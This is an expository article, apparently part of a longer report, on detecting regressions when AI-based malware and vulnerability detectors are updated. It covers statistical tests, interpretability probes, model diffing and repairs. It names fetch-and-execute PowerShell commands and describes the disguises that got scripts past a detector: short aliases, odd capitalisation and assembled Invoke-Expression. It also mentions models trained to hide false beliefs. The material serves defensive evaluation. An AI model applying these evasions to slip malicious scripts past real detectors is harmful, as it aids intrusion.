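The researchers distinguish regression from forgetting, which is a loss of average performance on older data. Forgetting relative to the previous version is the NFR minus the PFR on that data. If an update stops detecting three of every hundred old malware samples but starts detecting three others that the model used to miss, forgetting is zero and the NFR is 3%. Ordinary training allows this because it reduces the average error without protecting any particular correct answer. Some methods designed to prevent forgetting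 did no better than training on the new window alone, with malware NFRs of 3.40% and 3.46% on ELSA.

An antivirus product can still catch an exact copy of old malware by its signature, a stored pattern that identifies a known file, but it relies on the model to detect altered copies. A security regression therefore does the most practical harm when old malware has been modified, and this experiment did not create or separately test modified versions.

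### When attackers adapt to each version

Attackers can also look for new ways to fool the model after an update. Angioni, Demetrio and colleagues defined a measure for this in *Robustness-Congruent Adversarial Training for Secure Machine Learning Model Updates*. They first search for a change to an input that fools the current model, within a fixed limit on the size of the change. They then run a new search against the candidate, with the same limit but not necessarily the same changes. If the first search fails and the second succeeds, the input is a robustness negative flip.

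The researchers applied the measure to seven published image classifiers trained to resist such attacks. They used 2,000 small photographs and allowed only slight changes to each pixel. When a more robust model replaced a less robust one, about 2% to 6% of the images were robustness negative flips. In one replacement, the share of images that an attacker could get misclassified fell only from 41.55% to 40.65%, because 144 images became safe but 126 became vulnerable.

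These results are for image classifiers, and each "update" replaced one team's model with another's. Angioni and colleagues expect the same effect in malware and spam detection but did not test it. The measure also depends on the search. If the search against the current model gets stuck, an input that was always vulnerable will look like a new weakness in the candidate. Sun and colleagues saw large differences between repeated searches against one detector, so a security team using this measure should run several searches against each version.

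### Flips that occur without an update

The same model can give different answers to the same input. Setting the temperature to zero removes the random choice of tokens, but the tokens' scores can still vary slightly. Computers round the result of each addition, so adding the same numbers in a different order can give a slightly different total. Inference software often processes several inputs in a batch, and the batch size affects the order of the additions. If two tokens have almost equal scores, these rounding differences can change which one the model outputs.

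Nagisettygari and Sindiramutty (2026), in *How Much Determinism Can Fine-Tuning Buy?*, measured this effect in a Qwen model with half a billion parameters. They ran the same text through it twice, one passage at a time, and none of its 32,640 token choices changed. When they ran the passages in batches of 32, 62 choices (0.19%) changed. In all 62, the top two scores had been less than 0.05 apart.

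The effect of batching depended heavily on the number format. In a comparison on one type of graphics processor, batching changed no choices with 32-bit numbers, 45 with one common 16-bit format and 320 with another. Input length also mattered. In a related model, batching changed no scores for 512-token passages but more than half of the scores for 384-token passages in batches of 8 or 16. A team that tested only one length could wrongly conclude that its system always gives the same answers.

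Larger models also show the effect. *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026) describes a test of one prompt on an eight-billion-parameter model, run alone and in four kinds of batch. The answer changed only in the batch of eight, from the 58th token on. A single prompt can show that such changes happen, but not how often. *Understanding and Mitigating Numerical Sources of Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* (2025) found that the number and type of graphics processors can also change a model's answers, and recommends 32-bit numbers for anyone who relies on a single run. This takes about twice the memory and computing, and a 32-bit test is a poor guide to how a detector will behave when it runs in 16-bit.

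On a supplier's service, other customers' requests can affect the batch size. *Stochastic CHAOS* (2026) reports that Thinking Machines considers sensitivity to batching a main reason hosted models seem inconsistent.

This matters more for a detector that writes an explanation before its verdict than for one that outputs a single word, where only one token choice can change the verdict. An explanation involves hundreds of token choices, and an early change can alter the text that follows. When Nagisettygari and Sindiramutty had small models solve maths problems, 53.8% of the solutions differed somewhere between single and batched runs, though many of those differences may not have affected the final answer.

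Before comparing the current model with the candidate, the team measures the noise by running the current model on the whole suite several times and counting the flips between runs. These runs should include the batch sizes, server restarts and hardware that occur in production, because two runs under identical conditions could give zero flips and badly understate the noise. If the runs differ by two to six negative flips, almost all of the 90 in the example are due to the update, but if they differ by 40, noise could account for nearly half.

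The team can then run both models several more times on each case that flipped and keep those where the change persists. This removes false findings, but it can't recover changes that the original run failed to show. Cacioli (2026), in *Beyond the Mean*, put 2,000 multiple-choice questions to Llama 3 and Llama 3.1 ten times each, with random token sampling, and compared how often each model was right. A single run of each model at temperature zero had flagged 329 questions as changed, but 83 of these showed no reliable change over the ten runs. Of the 425 questions that did show a reliable change, the single run had not flagged 179. The 83 are a quarter of the flagged questions and only about 5% of the unchanged ones, although the abstract describes them as a quarter of all unchanged questions.

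Cacioli's count of 425 is probably too high because the method treated a difference of two correct answers out of ten as reliable for every question. When both models get a question right half the time, chance alone produces a difference that large about half the time. The general point still holds, and it suggests running small or important families several times in full, whether or not any case flipped.

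Repeated runs measure only how much a model's outputs vary from run to run. Retraining the candidate with another random seed would produce different flips between the current and candidate models, so the comparison describes this candidate, not the training method in general.

### Whether a loss extends beyond the suite

If the candidate misses a known attack every time, the team doesn't need a statistical test to show it. Kotawala (2026) points out in *Resolution Diagnostics for Paired LLM Evaluation* that a test is useful only when the cases stand for a larger population. For a security team, that population might be all the scripts an attacker could produce by applying a certain rewrite.

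McNemar's test is a standard method for paired results of this kind. It ignores every case on which both models are right or both are wrong, because those cases don't favour either model. If the two models were equally good, each remaining case would be as likely to be a negative flip as a positive one, like the toss of a coin. The p-value is the probability of a split at least as uneven as the one observed, in either direction. When all n flips go the same way,

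p = 2 × (1/2)ⁿ

The table shows the exact version of the test applied to Fetterman's results, with Llama as the current model and Foundation-Sec as the candidate. It also includes the worked example, assuming no positive flips in the family of 80.

| Comparison | Negative flips | Positive flips | p |
|---|---|---|---|
| Letter-case tier, 63 variants | 9 | 0 | 0.004 |
| Direct tier, 44 variants | 6 | 0 | 0.031 |
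| Short name for Invoke-WebRequest, 4 variants | 4 | 0 | 0.125 |
| Worked example, all 2,000 variants | 90 | 120 | 0.045 |
| Worked example, family of 80 | 60 | 0 | Below 0.001 |

The nine misses in the letter-case tier are unlikely to be chance by the common threshold of 0.05. The four misses of the short command name do not reach that threshold, but no result from four cases could, because reaching it takes at least six flips in one direction with none in the other. A team should not read a high p-value in a small family as a pass, because the test had little chance of detecting a change.

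In the worked example, the test favours the candidate on the whole suite but shows a severe loss on the family of 80. McNemar's test compares gains with losses, so a good overall result does not rule out a regression in one family.

A confidence interval is often more informative than a p-value because it gives the range of true rates that fit the result. For four misses in four, the 95% interval starts at 40%, because a model with that true miss rate would miss four in a row with probability 0.4⁴, or about 2.5%, the usual cut-off at each end of the interval. For Llama's 0 misses in 63, the interval extends to 5.7%, because a model with that miss rate would still catch 63 such variants in a row about 2.5% of the time. Foundation-Sec's 9 misses in 63 give an interval of roughly 7% to 25%. The two models' intervals do not overlap, but Llama's true miss rate could still be high enough to matter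 in practice.

### How many cases a comparison needs

The number of cases needed depends on how often the models disagree as well as on the difference in accuracy. Kotawala gives a formula for the number that provides an 80% chance of detecting a given difference at the 0.05 threshold. In terms of flips, it is

N = 7.85 × [NFR + PFR − (PFR − NFR)²] / (PFR − NFR)²

For the worked example, N is about 3,650, so a suite of 2,000 cases is too small to detect a gain of 1.5 points reliably, even though the p-value in this comparison fell just under 0.05. If the NFR were 0.5% and the PFR 2.0%, the gain would be the same, but about 860 cases would be enough because the update would change fewer answers.

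In 40 comparisons from a public ranking of language models, Kotawala found that pairing the two models' answers typically required less than half as many questions as treating their results as separate samples. Even so, 11 of the 40 comparisons had too few questions for the reported difference.

A team can calculate how many seeds a single family needs. Suppose the candidate misses a fifth of the attacks in a family that the current model catches completely. With one variant of each seed, the chance of seeing the six flips needed for significance is about 57% with 30 seeds and 84% with 40. Detecting smaller losses requires much larger families, so for most families a regression suite can reliably detect only severe regressions.

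### Variants of the same seed

All of these calculations assume that the cases are independent, but variants of one seed are not. Fetterman's nine letter-case misses may come from only a few scripts. If the team counts each seed once, the p-value is 0.008 if the misses come from eight seeds and 0.125 if they come from four.

A standard correction shows how much this can matter. If each seed has m variants and the results within a seed have a correlation of r, the number of cases is effectively smaller by a factor of

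1 + (m − 1)r

Suppose the 2,000 variants in the example come from 250 seeds with eight variants each, and r is 0.5. The factor is 4.5, so the suite carries about as much information as 444 independent cases. The p-value for the overall gain rises from 0.045 to about 0.33, and the team no longer has good evidence that the candidate is better.

The team can take the difference between the two models' scores on each seed and estimate the uncertainty from the spread of those differences. Alternatively, it can use a clustered standard error, which *Statistical Methods for Multiple Language Model Comparison on a Shared Evaluation* (2026) describes for questions that share a passage or a language. This method adds the correlation within each group to the usual estimate of error. Each seed and its variants can be treated as a group. The correction changed the results when Kotawala compared neighbouring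 models in the top ten of another ranking, using 12,032 questions. The number of pairs too close to separate reliably rose from four of nine to six after allowing for similarity between questions on the same subject.

### Testing many families

Checking every family separately is the best way to find a concentrated loss, but it also produces false alarms. If a team tests 20 unaffected families and each test has a 5% chance of a false alarm, the chance of at least one is 1 − 0.95²⁰, or 64%. The true figure is usually lower when the families are small, because a family with fewer than six flips can't trigger an alarm.

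The simplest correction divides the threshold by the number of tests, which gives 0.0025 for 20 families. With no positive flips, a family then needs ten negative ones to count as a regression, instead of six. Holm's method gives the same protection with somewhat less loss of sensitivity. The Benjamini-Hochberg method is more lenient and limits the expected share of false alarms among the families it flags. *evalci* (2026), a software library for comparing language models, offers both and applies them to every comparison the user runs. This prevents a user from testing 20 families and correcting only for the three that looked interesting.

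A strict correction is appropriate for claiming that the candidate is worse on a family, but it is too conservative for choosing which families to investigate. A false alarm takes some analyst time, while an overlooked regression can let an attack through. The team can therefore investigate any family where the loss is significant at the ordinary 0.05 level, or even where the candidate repeatably misses a single case. It then writes new variants from seeds that weren't in the first test and runs both models on them. If the first result was chance, the new cases should show no consistent loss. If the candidate misses those too, the team has evidence from separate scripts and has to correct only for the few families it retested.

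## Checking the model's internals for changed use of evidence

Comparing answers case by case finds losses only in the cases the team has written. A team that has the weights of both versions can also examine their internals to see whether the candidate relies on different evidence, and use the findings to choose which commands to test next. In *Understanding AI from the Inside*, Barez, Wu and colleagues (2026) survey this field, which they call mechanistic interpretability and which studies how a neural network's internal mechanisms relate to its behaviour. They consider it unclear whether current methods can deal with the failures that behavioural tests handle poorly.

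### From script to label

A language model first turns each token of a script into a list of numbers called the token's embedding. In Llama 3.1 8B and the models built on it, each list has 4,096 numbers and passes through 32 layers, numbered 0 to 31. Each layer has 32 attention heads, which bring in information from earlier tokens, and a feed-forward block, which transforms the information at each token separately. For example, an attention head might bring the name of a download command to the position of the web address that follows it. Every head and block adds its result to a running list called the residual stream. After the last layer, the model converts this list into scores for possible answers, and the gap between the scores for "malicious" and "benign" determines the label.

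Two models can give the same label for different reasons. Suppose a script's command name adds 3 points to the current model's gap and the rest of the script adds 1. In the candidate, the command name subtracts 1 point and the rest adds 5. Both gaps are 4, so a held-out test shows no difference, but rewriting the script to weaken the evidence outside the command name would hurt the candidate far more. Real contributions don't add up this neatly, but removing the command name and measuring the gap again would reveal the difference before anyone had written such a variant. When training changes how a model encodes and uses evidence in this way, the change is called representation drift.

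### The route Fetterman traced

Fetterman looked for the circuit, or set of model parts, that carries evidence of malice in Foundation-Sec. Fetterman first looked for attention heads that consistently focus on suspicious commands and web addresses, and ran rough tests that disabled single heads or whole bands of layers. Two stricter tests then used the main collection of 293 script pairs. Path patching replaces the output of chosen heads on one script with their output on its partner, and head ablation disables the heads. If the malicious score drops sharply after either change, the model was depending on those heads.

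The simplest route ran from one head in Layer 0 to three heads in Layer 12. Before patching, the average gap in favour of "malicious" was 4.71. Patching this route reduced the gap by 3.61, or 77%, and changed the label in 87 of the 293 pairs. Patching a group of four Layer 12 heads reduced the gap by 3.82, or 81%, and also changed 87 labels. Disabling the same four heads reduced the gap by only 1.89.

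These effects are large, but about 70% of the labels stayed the same, so other parts of the model also carry useful evidence. Fetterman presents patching mainly as a test of whether the route alone can recreate a malicious label. But in the published figures, the malicious score falls, which is more direct evidence that the model depends on the route.

The average also depends heavily on one family, DownloadFile, which accounts for half the pairs and two-thirds of the total effect of patching the simplest route. The reductions were only 1.92 for Invoke-WebRequest and 1.46 for Invoke-Expression, two of the commands involved in the later misses. Patching changed no labels in the seven pairs with -EncodedCommand.

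Llama uses much the same route as Foundation-Sec but spreads it across more heads. The same Layer 0 head stood out in 14 of the 18 pairs that Fetterman used in the search, and Layer 12 again combined the evidence. On 74 pairs, patching three increasingly broad routes in Llama changed 11, 18 and 36 labels. Patching comparable routes in Foundation-Sec changed 24, about 25 and about 25.

Fetterman concludes that Foundation-Sec inherited the route from Llama and that security training concentrated it. But Foundation-Sec and the finished Llama model were both built from Llama 3.1 8B, so it is more likely that both inherited the route from there. Testing Llama 3.1 8B itself would settle the question.

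The same methods suggest how disguised scripts got past Foundation-Sec. In the four missed scripts that used "iwr", the Layer 12 heads still produced evidence of malice, but feed-forward blocks before Layer 13 added an opposing signal, and the combined evidence at that point favoured "benign". Fetterman found the same pattern in the four missed scripts that assembled Invoke-Expression from pieces of text. In Llama, the combined evidence just before Layer 13 still favoured "malicious". No single block explains the reversal, and this explanation is based on eight variants made with two kinds of rewrite.

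### The linear probe

Tracing a circuit takes specialist work, so Fetterman proposes a cheaper check at the same point in the model. A linear probe is a simple formula that estimates a quantity from a model's internal state:

estimate = w · x + b

Here, x is the residual stream just before Layer 13, w is a list of 4,096 weights, and b is a constant. The estimate is of how strongly a particular Layer 12 head pushes the model towards "malicious".

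Fetterman fitted a probe for each of four heads in Llama, using 206 malicious scripts. A probe with far more weights than scripts to learn from can fit those scripts perfectly and still be useless on new ones. Fetterman therefore used ridge regression, which penalises large weights, and repeatedly fitted each probe on four-fifths of the scripts and tested it on the rest. The probes' estimates correlated with the measured values at 0.80 to 0.87. Some of this correlation is expected, because the residual stream before Layer 13 already contains what the Layer 12 heads added.

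To check an update, the team fits the probe on the current model, then runs the current and updated models on the same ordinary scripts. It applies the same w and b to both models and averages the estimates by family. The families whose averages differ most between the two models are the first candidates for new variants.

The probe is much less informative about individual scripts. Fetterman used Llama's internal state to predict how far Foundation-Sec's score on each script depended on the circuit, and the predictions had a correlation of 0.41 with the measured values. They explained about 17% of the variation between scripts, compared with 64% to 76% for the original task within Llama. Cisco therefore describes the output as a ranked list of command families, not a prediction for each script. Neither correlation shows whether the families that drift most also have the most misses.

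Alpman and Altun (2026), in *Train Once, Transfer Where?*, found a similar contrast when they moved probes between six language models. They measured performance by AUC, the chance that a probe scores a random positive example above a random negative one, so guessing gives 0.5. Probes for properties of the input, such as whether a prompt was unsafe, kept 94% to 99.5% of their advantage over guessing on the main tasks. Probes for the receiving model's behaviour did worse. For example, the AUC of one type of probe fell from 0.82 to 0.62 when the task was to predict whether a model would change its answer to match a user's opinion. How much Foundation-Sec depends on a circuit is also a property of the model rather than the script, so a low correlation is unsurprising.

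A model's internals can change substantially without a loss of function. Tsatsos (2026), in *Linear Probes Transfer from Base to Distilled Language Models despite Rotation*, trained probes for harmful requests on four base models and applied them unchanged to eight successors. The direction separating unsafe from safe prompts had turned by 17° to 35°, yet the probes' AUC changed by only −0.011 to +0.027 on the main test. In Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, one of the successors, the direction had turned by 24° and the probe did slightly better than on the base model. In the successors trained on another model's reasoning, directions unrelated to safety had turned by similar amounts.

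A team therefore needs to know how much drift is normal. It can measure the drift between two candidates trained on the same data with different random seeds, and prioritize families that drift clearly more than that.

### The indicator-token sign test

Fetterman's second check doesn't require a map of the circuit. It uses indicator tokens, the parts of a script that name a suspicious command such as Invoke-WebRequest. For each malicious script, the team takes these steps with both models:

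1. Record the gap between the "malicious" and "benign" scores.
2. Replace the embeddings of the indicator tokens with the average embedding of the model's whole vocabulary, and leave the rest of the script unchanged.
3. Record the new gap and subtract the old one from it.
4. Average these differences for each family.

If a script's gap falls from 4.0 to 2.5, the difference is −1.5, which means the command name was pushing the model towards "malicious". Fetterman calls such a token a driver. If the difference is positive, the name was lowering the malicious score and is a suppressor. It is a warning sign if a family's command name is a driver in the current model but a suppressor in the candidate.

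For the 19 Invoke-WebRequest pairs, the average was −1.60 in Llama and +1.13 in Foundation-Sec. No other family reversed so clearly, and Foundation-Sec later missed all four variants that used the command's short name.

If the full name lowers Foundation-Sec's malicious score, replacing it with "iwr" should make the script easier to detect, not harder. Fetterman's explanation is that the short name also disrupts the evidence from the surrounding text, and that this loss outweighs the gain. That may be right, but the sign test shows only that the two models treat the full command name differently. It doesn't measure how the short name affects the evidence from the surrounding text.

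The sample is also small. The difference was positive for 14 of the 19 Invoke-WebRequest scripts (73.7%), which gives a p-value of about 0.06. The average embedding corresponds to no real token, so a model may respond to it differently than to inputs in normal use. A team could repeat the test with an ordinary neutral word in place of the command.

### What the checks can and cannot guide

The family that the sign test flagged accounts for 4 of Foundation-Sec's 19 misses. Another 13 involved Invoke-Expression or its short form IEX, and the test flagged neither. A team that wrote variants only for the flagged family would have overlooked most of the known failures.

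One correct choice is also weak evidence for the method. At least three of the seven families had misses, so a random pick would have had at least a 43% chance of choosing a family with misses. Fetterman tried the checks on only one pair of models. A convincing trial would run the checks on many updates, publish the ranking of families for each update before anyone tested variants, and compare the rankings with the misses.

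Because Foundation-Sec's misses changed with the prompt, the team should run both checks with the prompt it will use in production.

Both checks require the model's weights, or at least access to its internal states, which suppliers' online services rarely provide. If the base model changes, the probe may also stop working, because its 4,096 weights may not fit the new model or may no longer mean the same thing. The sign test still works because the team measures each model separately and compares only the results.

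The checks are quick enough to help decide what to test first. For the imaginary PowerShell team's 500 malicious seeds, the sign test takes 2,000 runs (two per seed on each model), or a little over an hour at the speed Splunk reported. The team might then write 80 of its 200 new variants for the families with the most drift or a changed sign, and spread the other 120 over the rest. Families with clean results stay in the regression suite, because Invoke-Expression would also have looked clean.

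### Finding differences nobody suspected

Fetterman's sign test needs a list of commands to examine. Model diffing compares two models' internal states or outputs to find differences that nobody specified in advance.

The simplest internal method averages the difference between the two models' states on the same text. *Narrow Finetuning Leaves Clearly Readable Traces in Activation Differences* (2025) used such differences to recover what a model had been trained on. *Diff Mining* (Kocher, West and colleagues, 2026) reports that this method works less well when developers mix unrelated data into the training, as many security teams would.

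A crosscoder instead learns one dictionary of features for both models, where a feature is a recurring pattern in their internal states. Researchers then look for features that belong mainly to one model. *Delta-Crosscoder* (Kassem, Jiralerspong and colleagues, 2026) explains that ordinary crosscoders tend to overlook narrow changes because only a limited number of features can be active at once, and features shared by both models take most of the places. The paper's version adds a penalty for failing to reproduce the difference between the models.

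Researchers tested the crosscoder method on ten models with planted changes, such as false facts or a secret word. In all ten, it found features that altered the planted behaviour when strengthened or weakened. The researchers examined only the three highest-ranked features for each model, so this success rate doesn't show how many false leads a longer list would contain. Training each crosscoder also took about 200 million tokens of text, which is far more work than training a linear probe.

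*Cross-Architecture Model Diffing with Crosscoders* (2026) extends the approach to models with different designs, which could help when a team replaces its base model. The method found, for example, a feature behind one model's refusals to reproduce copyrighted text. *What Does an LLM Learn from Reinforcement Learning?* (2026) applies one fixed dictionary to successive versions of a model and measures how each feature's average activity changes, much as Fetterman reuses one probe.

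Kocher and colleagues' own method needs only the scores that the original and fine-tuned models give to possible next tokens. It runs both models on ordinary web text, finds the tokens whose scores rose most after fine-tuning at each position, and lists those that appear most often. They tested it on a 70-billion-parameter model that other researchers had trained to hold 52 false beliefs and then hide them. The list contained tokens related to at least a third of the beliefs. Some results reflected the format of the training data rather than its subject. For a model trained on documents about cake baking and code comments, one group of tokens was almost entirely capitalised words, reflecting the documents' headings.

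Other methods compare the models' written output. Kempf, Schrodi and colleagues (2026), in *Simple LLM Baselines are Competitive for Model Diffing*, collected two models' answers to 1,000 real user prompts and had a language model describe the differences. They also tried a method based on a feature dictionary. They tested the descriptions on 500 new prompts, measuring how often each one pointed to the right model when it applied. Guessing would give 50%.

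Average accuracy was above 87% for both methods in two experiments with planted behaviours. Between two revisions of Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, it was 63.4% for the language model's descriptions and 72.3% for the other method, so roughly a third of the applicable judgements had the direction wrong. Both methods also missed one planted behaviour, an assumption that the user is a woman, and instead reported side effects of the training, such as shorter answers. Only 57 of the 1,000 prompts were well suited to revealing the assumption, and even those rarely revealed it.

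Pope, Thibodeau and colleagues (2026), in *Automatically Finding and Validating Unexpected Side-Effects of Interventions on Language Models*, control false leads more strictly. One language model reads sample answers and describes a possible difference between the models that wrote them. Another uses that description to judge which model wrote each new answer, without being told. The researchers keep a description only if it passes a statistical test, using the Benjamini-Hochberg method with a limit of 5%. They planted 36 personas in a model, ran the method four times on each, and recovered the persona every time.

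They then studied three real changes to language models. The table gives the average number of descriptions that passed over three runs:

| Change to the model | Statements about personality and values (135 descriptions) | Unfinished Wikipedia sentences (50) | Questions about common misconceptions (15) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Training on another model's reasoning | 108 | 25 | 13 |
| Editing ten stored facts | 41 | 37 | 13 |
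| Removing knowledge of Harry Potter | 0 | 10 | 1 |

The edited model resembles a detector with a regression that a benchmark can miss. Its results on a yes-or-no benchmark barely changed, but its longer answers often drifted to the politics of Albania or the Soviet Union, probably because the edits included facts such as Albania's capital. In the Harry Potter results, one set of prompts revealed no side effects and another revealed ten, so the choice of prompts matters a great deal.

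The 5% limit also covers only whether a description helps to tell the two models apart, so a description can pass even if some of its details are wrong. A team can check the rate of false leads on its own data by comparing the current model with an identical copy, since any difference reported between them is false.

None of these experiments tested for missed malware. The text-comparison methods have almost nothing to describe when a detector outputs one word, and general user prompts are unlikely to reveal how a model treats Invoke-Expression. If a team's model explains its verdicts, the team could apply Pope and colleagues' method to explanations of its own scripts, grouped by threat family, for about nine US cents per description. But they warn that their method samples typical answers and may miss rare or adversarial failures, which are the ones attackers look for.

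## Repairing a regression without causing another

A team that has confirmed a regression can repair it outside the model, in the prompt, or in the weights. Any repair that changes the model's answers is another update, so the team has to check it for new regressions. The table lists the repairs from least to most effort.

| Repair | When it fits | Main risk |
|---|---|---|
| Rule or input normalisation | The missed attacks share a pattern that a simple program can recognise or undo | Misses any disguise the program doesn't cover |
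| Prompt change | The same model catches the attacks when the instructions differ | Moves the misses to other attacks |
| More training data | The missed attacks resemble few scripts in the training data | Teaches the model one disguise and no others |
| Constrained update | The candidate has scattered losses on cases the current model handles well | Preserves the current model's blind spots too |
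| Fresh start from an earlier version | The training data is wrong or poisoned, or many families got worse | Gives up the update's gains until retraining succeeds |

### Repairs outside the model

Input normalization converts each script to a standard form before the model reads it. For PowerShell, a program can replace short command names with full ones and restore the usual capitalization. Thirteen of Foundation-Sec's 19 misses involved only a short name or changed capitalization. Restoring the original spelling would have prevented all 13, because the model had detected every seed. The other six misses involved commands that the script assembled or called indirectly, and undoing those changes requires a program that can partly evaluate the script.

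All lower case would be a simpler standard form, but Foundation-Sec missed one of the four scripts with Invoke-Expression in lower case. Converting everything to lower case would also corrupt Base64 text, where capital and small letters have different values. Normalisation also erases strange capitalisation, which is a sign of disguise, so the team might check the original script with a separate rule.

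Sun and colleagues found that cleaning the input to vulnerable-code detectors helped only against misleading text in comments and preprocessor directives, not against renamed variables or code that never runs. They also tried randomized smoothing, which combines a model's answers on many randomly altered copies of an input, but it lowered the attacks' success rate by only 1.6 to 8.9 percentage points.

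A detection rule can raise an alert whenever a script matches a known attack, regardless of the model's answer. Such a rule can't create a miss, so it is a good first response to an attack in progress. It will add false alarms if its pattern is too broad, for example if it matches every use of "iwr".

The team can also keep the current model running beside the candidate and raise an alert if either one labels a script malicious. In the earlier example with 2,000 malicious variants, the two models together would catch 1,920, compared with 1,830 for the candidate alone, with no security regressions. Running both takes twice the computing and produces every false alarm that either model raises. *Multimodal Abstention That Preserves Acquired Correct Answers* (2026) describes choosing between old and new predictions, or combining them, as an established way to limit regressions.

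Sheng and Lu built a proof of concept that sends only high-risk inputs back to the old model. No single warning sign worked best across their tasks and updates, and combining signs rarely helped. Several signs require running both models on the input, and if the detector outputs one label, a team could just compare the two models' labels instead.

### Why a prompt fix needs a full re-run

A new prompt costs almost nothing to write and is easy to undo. Fetterman tried one that told Foundation-Sec to judge a script by its overall purpose instead of by individual commands. The model then caught all four scripts with the short name "iwr", which it had missed under the plain prompt. But it began to miss disguised versions of Invoke-Expression that it had caught before, and it did worse on changed capitalization. This table covers the 43 letter-case variants that don't use the short name IEX:

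| Rewrite | Misses, plain prompt | Misses, purpose prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Invoke-Expression, alternating case | 4 of 4 | 4 of 4 |
| Invoke-Expression, lower case | 1 of 4 | 4 of 4 |
| DownloadString, lower case | 0 of 4 | 2 of 4 |
| DownloadString, alternating case | 0 of 6 | 2 of 6 |
| All others | 0 of 25 | 0 of 25 |
| Total | 5 of 43 | 12 of 43 |

The new prompt caused seven negative flips in this group and no positive ones. If the seven were independent, McNemar's test would give a p-value of 0.016, though some probably share a seed. A team that re-tested only the four "iwr" scripts would have recorded the regression as fully repaired.

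Llama missed none of the variants under either prompt, which suggests that Foundation-Sec's weakness lies in its weights and that rewording the prompt mostly changes where the weakness appears. A prompt change is still worth trying if the team then runs the whole suite, the held-out set and the prompt-injection tests. Engineers who choose among many prompts by suite score should confirm their choice on the secret cases.

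### Training on the missed variants

The obvious repair in the weights is to add the missed variants to the training data, along with benign scripts rewritten the same way.

Risse and Böhme (2023), in *Uncovering the Limits of Machine Learning for Automatic Vulnerability Detection*, tested how far this kind of training carries over. They used two datasets, six language models that were among the best vulnerability detectors of their time, and 11 ways of rewriting code without changing its behaviour. They first measured how much a detector's score fell when they applied one rewrite to the test functions. They then retrained the detector on functions with the same rewrite and, separately, on functions with a different one, for every pair of rewrites.

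Training on the same rewrite restored 69.0% of the lost score on one dataset and 66.2% on the other, but training on a different rewrite increased the loss by 30.2% and 77.5%, respectively. Earlier researchers had reported that robustness carried over between rewrites, but they had trained and tested on closely related ones, such as two ways of renaming variables.

These results show how a suite can lose its value. Suppose a suite has ten kinds of rewrite with 100 cases each, and the model misses 20 cases of each kind. The team trains on five of the kinds, and the effects match those on Risse and Böhme's first dataset:

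| | Misses before | Misses after |
|---|---|---|
| Five kinds used in training | 100 of 500 | about 31 of 500 |
| Five kinds not used | 100 of 500 | about 130 of 500 |
| Whole suite | 200 of 1,000 | about 161 of 1,000 |

The suite's overall score rises from 80% to 84%, even though the model has become worse at catching disguises it wasn't trained on. New cases written from fresh seeds would not reveal this decline if the team used the same five rewrites. Once a kind of rewrite has entered the training data, the team needs to report results on it separately and keep some other kinds out of training.

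Later work on newer models gives little reason to expect that a few examples will make a model broadly robust. *Revisiting Pre-trained Language Models for Vulnerability Detection* (2025) applied four rewrites to test functions, and most models did worse to varying degrees. They handled converted loops and reversed comparisons moderately well, so a good result on one rewrite does not reliably predict the result on another. Sun and colleagues used adversarial fine-tuning, which trains a model on inputs altered to fool it. Complete Resistance, the share of detected flaws that the model still caught after every rewrite, rose only from 0.13% to 3.88%, and the model lost some accuracy. Training on written reasoning made the detectors in TrapEval more consistent when code was rewritten but lowered their recall.

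Risse and Böhme's detectors are several generations old, so the effect in a current model could be smaller or larger. A team can measure it by leaving one kind of rewrite out of training, testing on that kind, and then repeating this with another kind.

### Replaying old data

Training only on new examples can make a model forget old ones. *MADAR* (Rahman, Coull and colleagues, 2025) describes how an attacker could exploit this in a "retrograde malware attack". If the defender updates a detector with only the latest samples, each update makes it more likely to miss older malware. The attacker can then bring back an old program, perhaps slightly modified, and get past the detector.

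Old malware comes and goes. In the Windows collection that Rahman and colleagues studied, only 551 of the 913 malware families that appeared in January 2018 appeared again in February. Training only on February's samples would give the model no examples of the other 362.

Replay counters forgetting by mixing stored examples into each new round of training. MADAR chooses them by malware family. Within each family, half are typical samples and half are unusual ones, which an algorithm identifies by how easily it can separate them from the rest. The researchers updated a small neural network month by month and averaged its accuracy over all the months so far:

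| Old files replayed | Accuracy, random choice | Accuracy, MADAR |
|---|---|---|
| None | 93.1% | 93.1% |
| 10,000 | 94.1% | 94.7% |
| 50,000 | 95.3% | 95.4% |
| 200,000 | 95.9% | 96.0% |
| All | 96.4% | 96.4% |

For telling malware from benign files, the number of stored examples mattered far more than how the researchers chose them. Careful selection helped more with naming the malware's family. With 20,000 stored examples, MADAR reached an average accuracy of 85.8%, compared with 66.8% for the best earlier method. These averages don't measure how many attacks the model stopped detecting after each update.

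*Regression-aware Continual Learning for Android Malware Detection* measured the negative flip rate (NFR) on malware. Replaying 200 old apps lowered it from 3.17% to 2.76% on the ELSA collection and from 2.92% to 2.28% on the larger TESSERACT. Retraining on all the old apps lowered it much further.

If the old data fits within the training budget, the team should use all of it, as the imaginary PowerShell team already does. The team needs to select a subset when the archive runs to millions of files or when privacy rules force it to delete some of them.

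### Positive-congruent training

Replay reminds the model of the correct labels. A constrained update also penalises the model for moving away from its predecessor's answers. The best-known version is positive-congruent training, which Yan and colleagues introduced for image classifiers in 2021 and Ghiani and colleagues later applied to Android malware. Training minimises this sum over all examples:

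Σ [ L(yᵢ, f(xᵢ)) + λ · wᵢ · ½‖f(xᵢ) − f_old(xᵢ)‖² ]

- L is the ordinary training loss, which is large when the new model f gives the correct label yᵢ a low score on input xᵢ.
- ‖f(xᵢ) − f_old(xᵢ)‖² is the squared distance between the new and old models' scores for the possible labels. The old model stays fixed.
- wᵢ is α + β if the old model labelled the example correctly and α if it did not.
- λ sets how much the whole penalty counts against the ordinary loss.

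Suppose the old model correctly classified a malicious script, scoring it −1 for "benign" and 3 for "malicious", and the new model scores it 0.5 for both. Half the squared distance between the two models' scores is (1.5² + 2.5²)/2 = 4.25. Ghiani and colleagues set α to 1 and β to 0.5, so the penalty before multiplying by λ is (1 + 0.5) × 4.25, or about 6.4. If the old model had misclassified the script, the penalty for the same change would be 4.25.

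They combined the penalty with several training methods. The table shows one of them, synaptic intelligence, which discourages changes to weights that were important for earlier data. The table also includes retraining on all the old data without the penalty.

| Collection and training | Malware NFR | Recall, past and current apps | Recall, current and future apps |
|---|---|---|---|
| ELSA, synaptic intelligence | 3.40% | 83.87% | 79.29% |
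| ELSA, with penalty | 1.19% | 83.09% | 78.23% |
| ELSA, all old data | 1.16% | 87.08% | 80.54% |
| TESSERACT, synaptic intelligence | 2.92% | 85.01% | 70.64% |
| TESSERACT, with penalty | 1.75% | 81.18% | 61.98% |
| TESSERACT, all old data | 0.54% | 92.28% | 71.11% |

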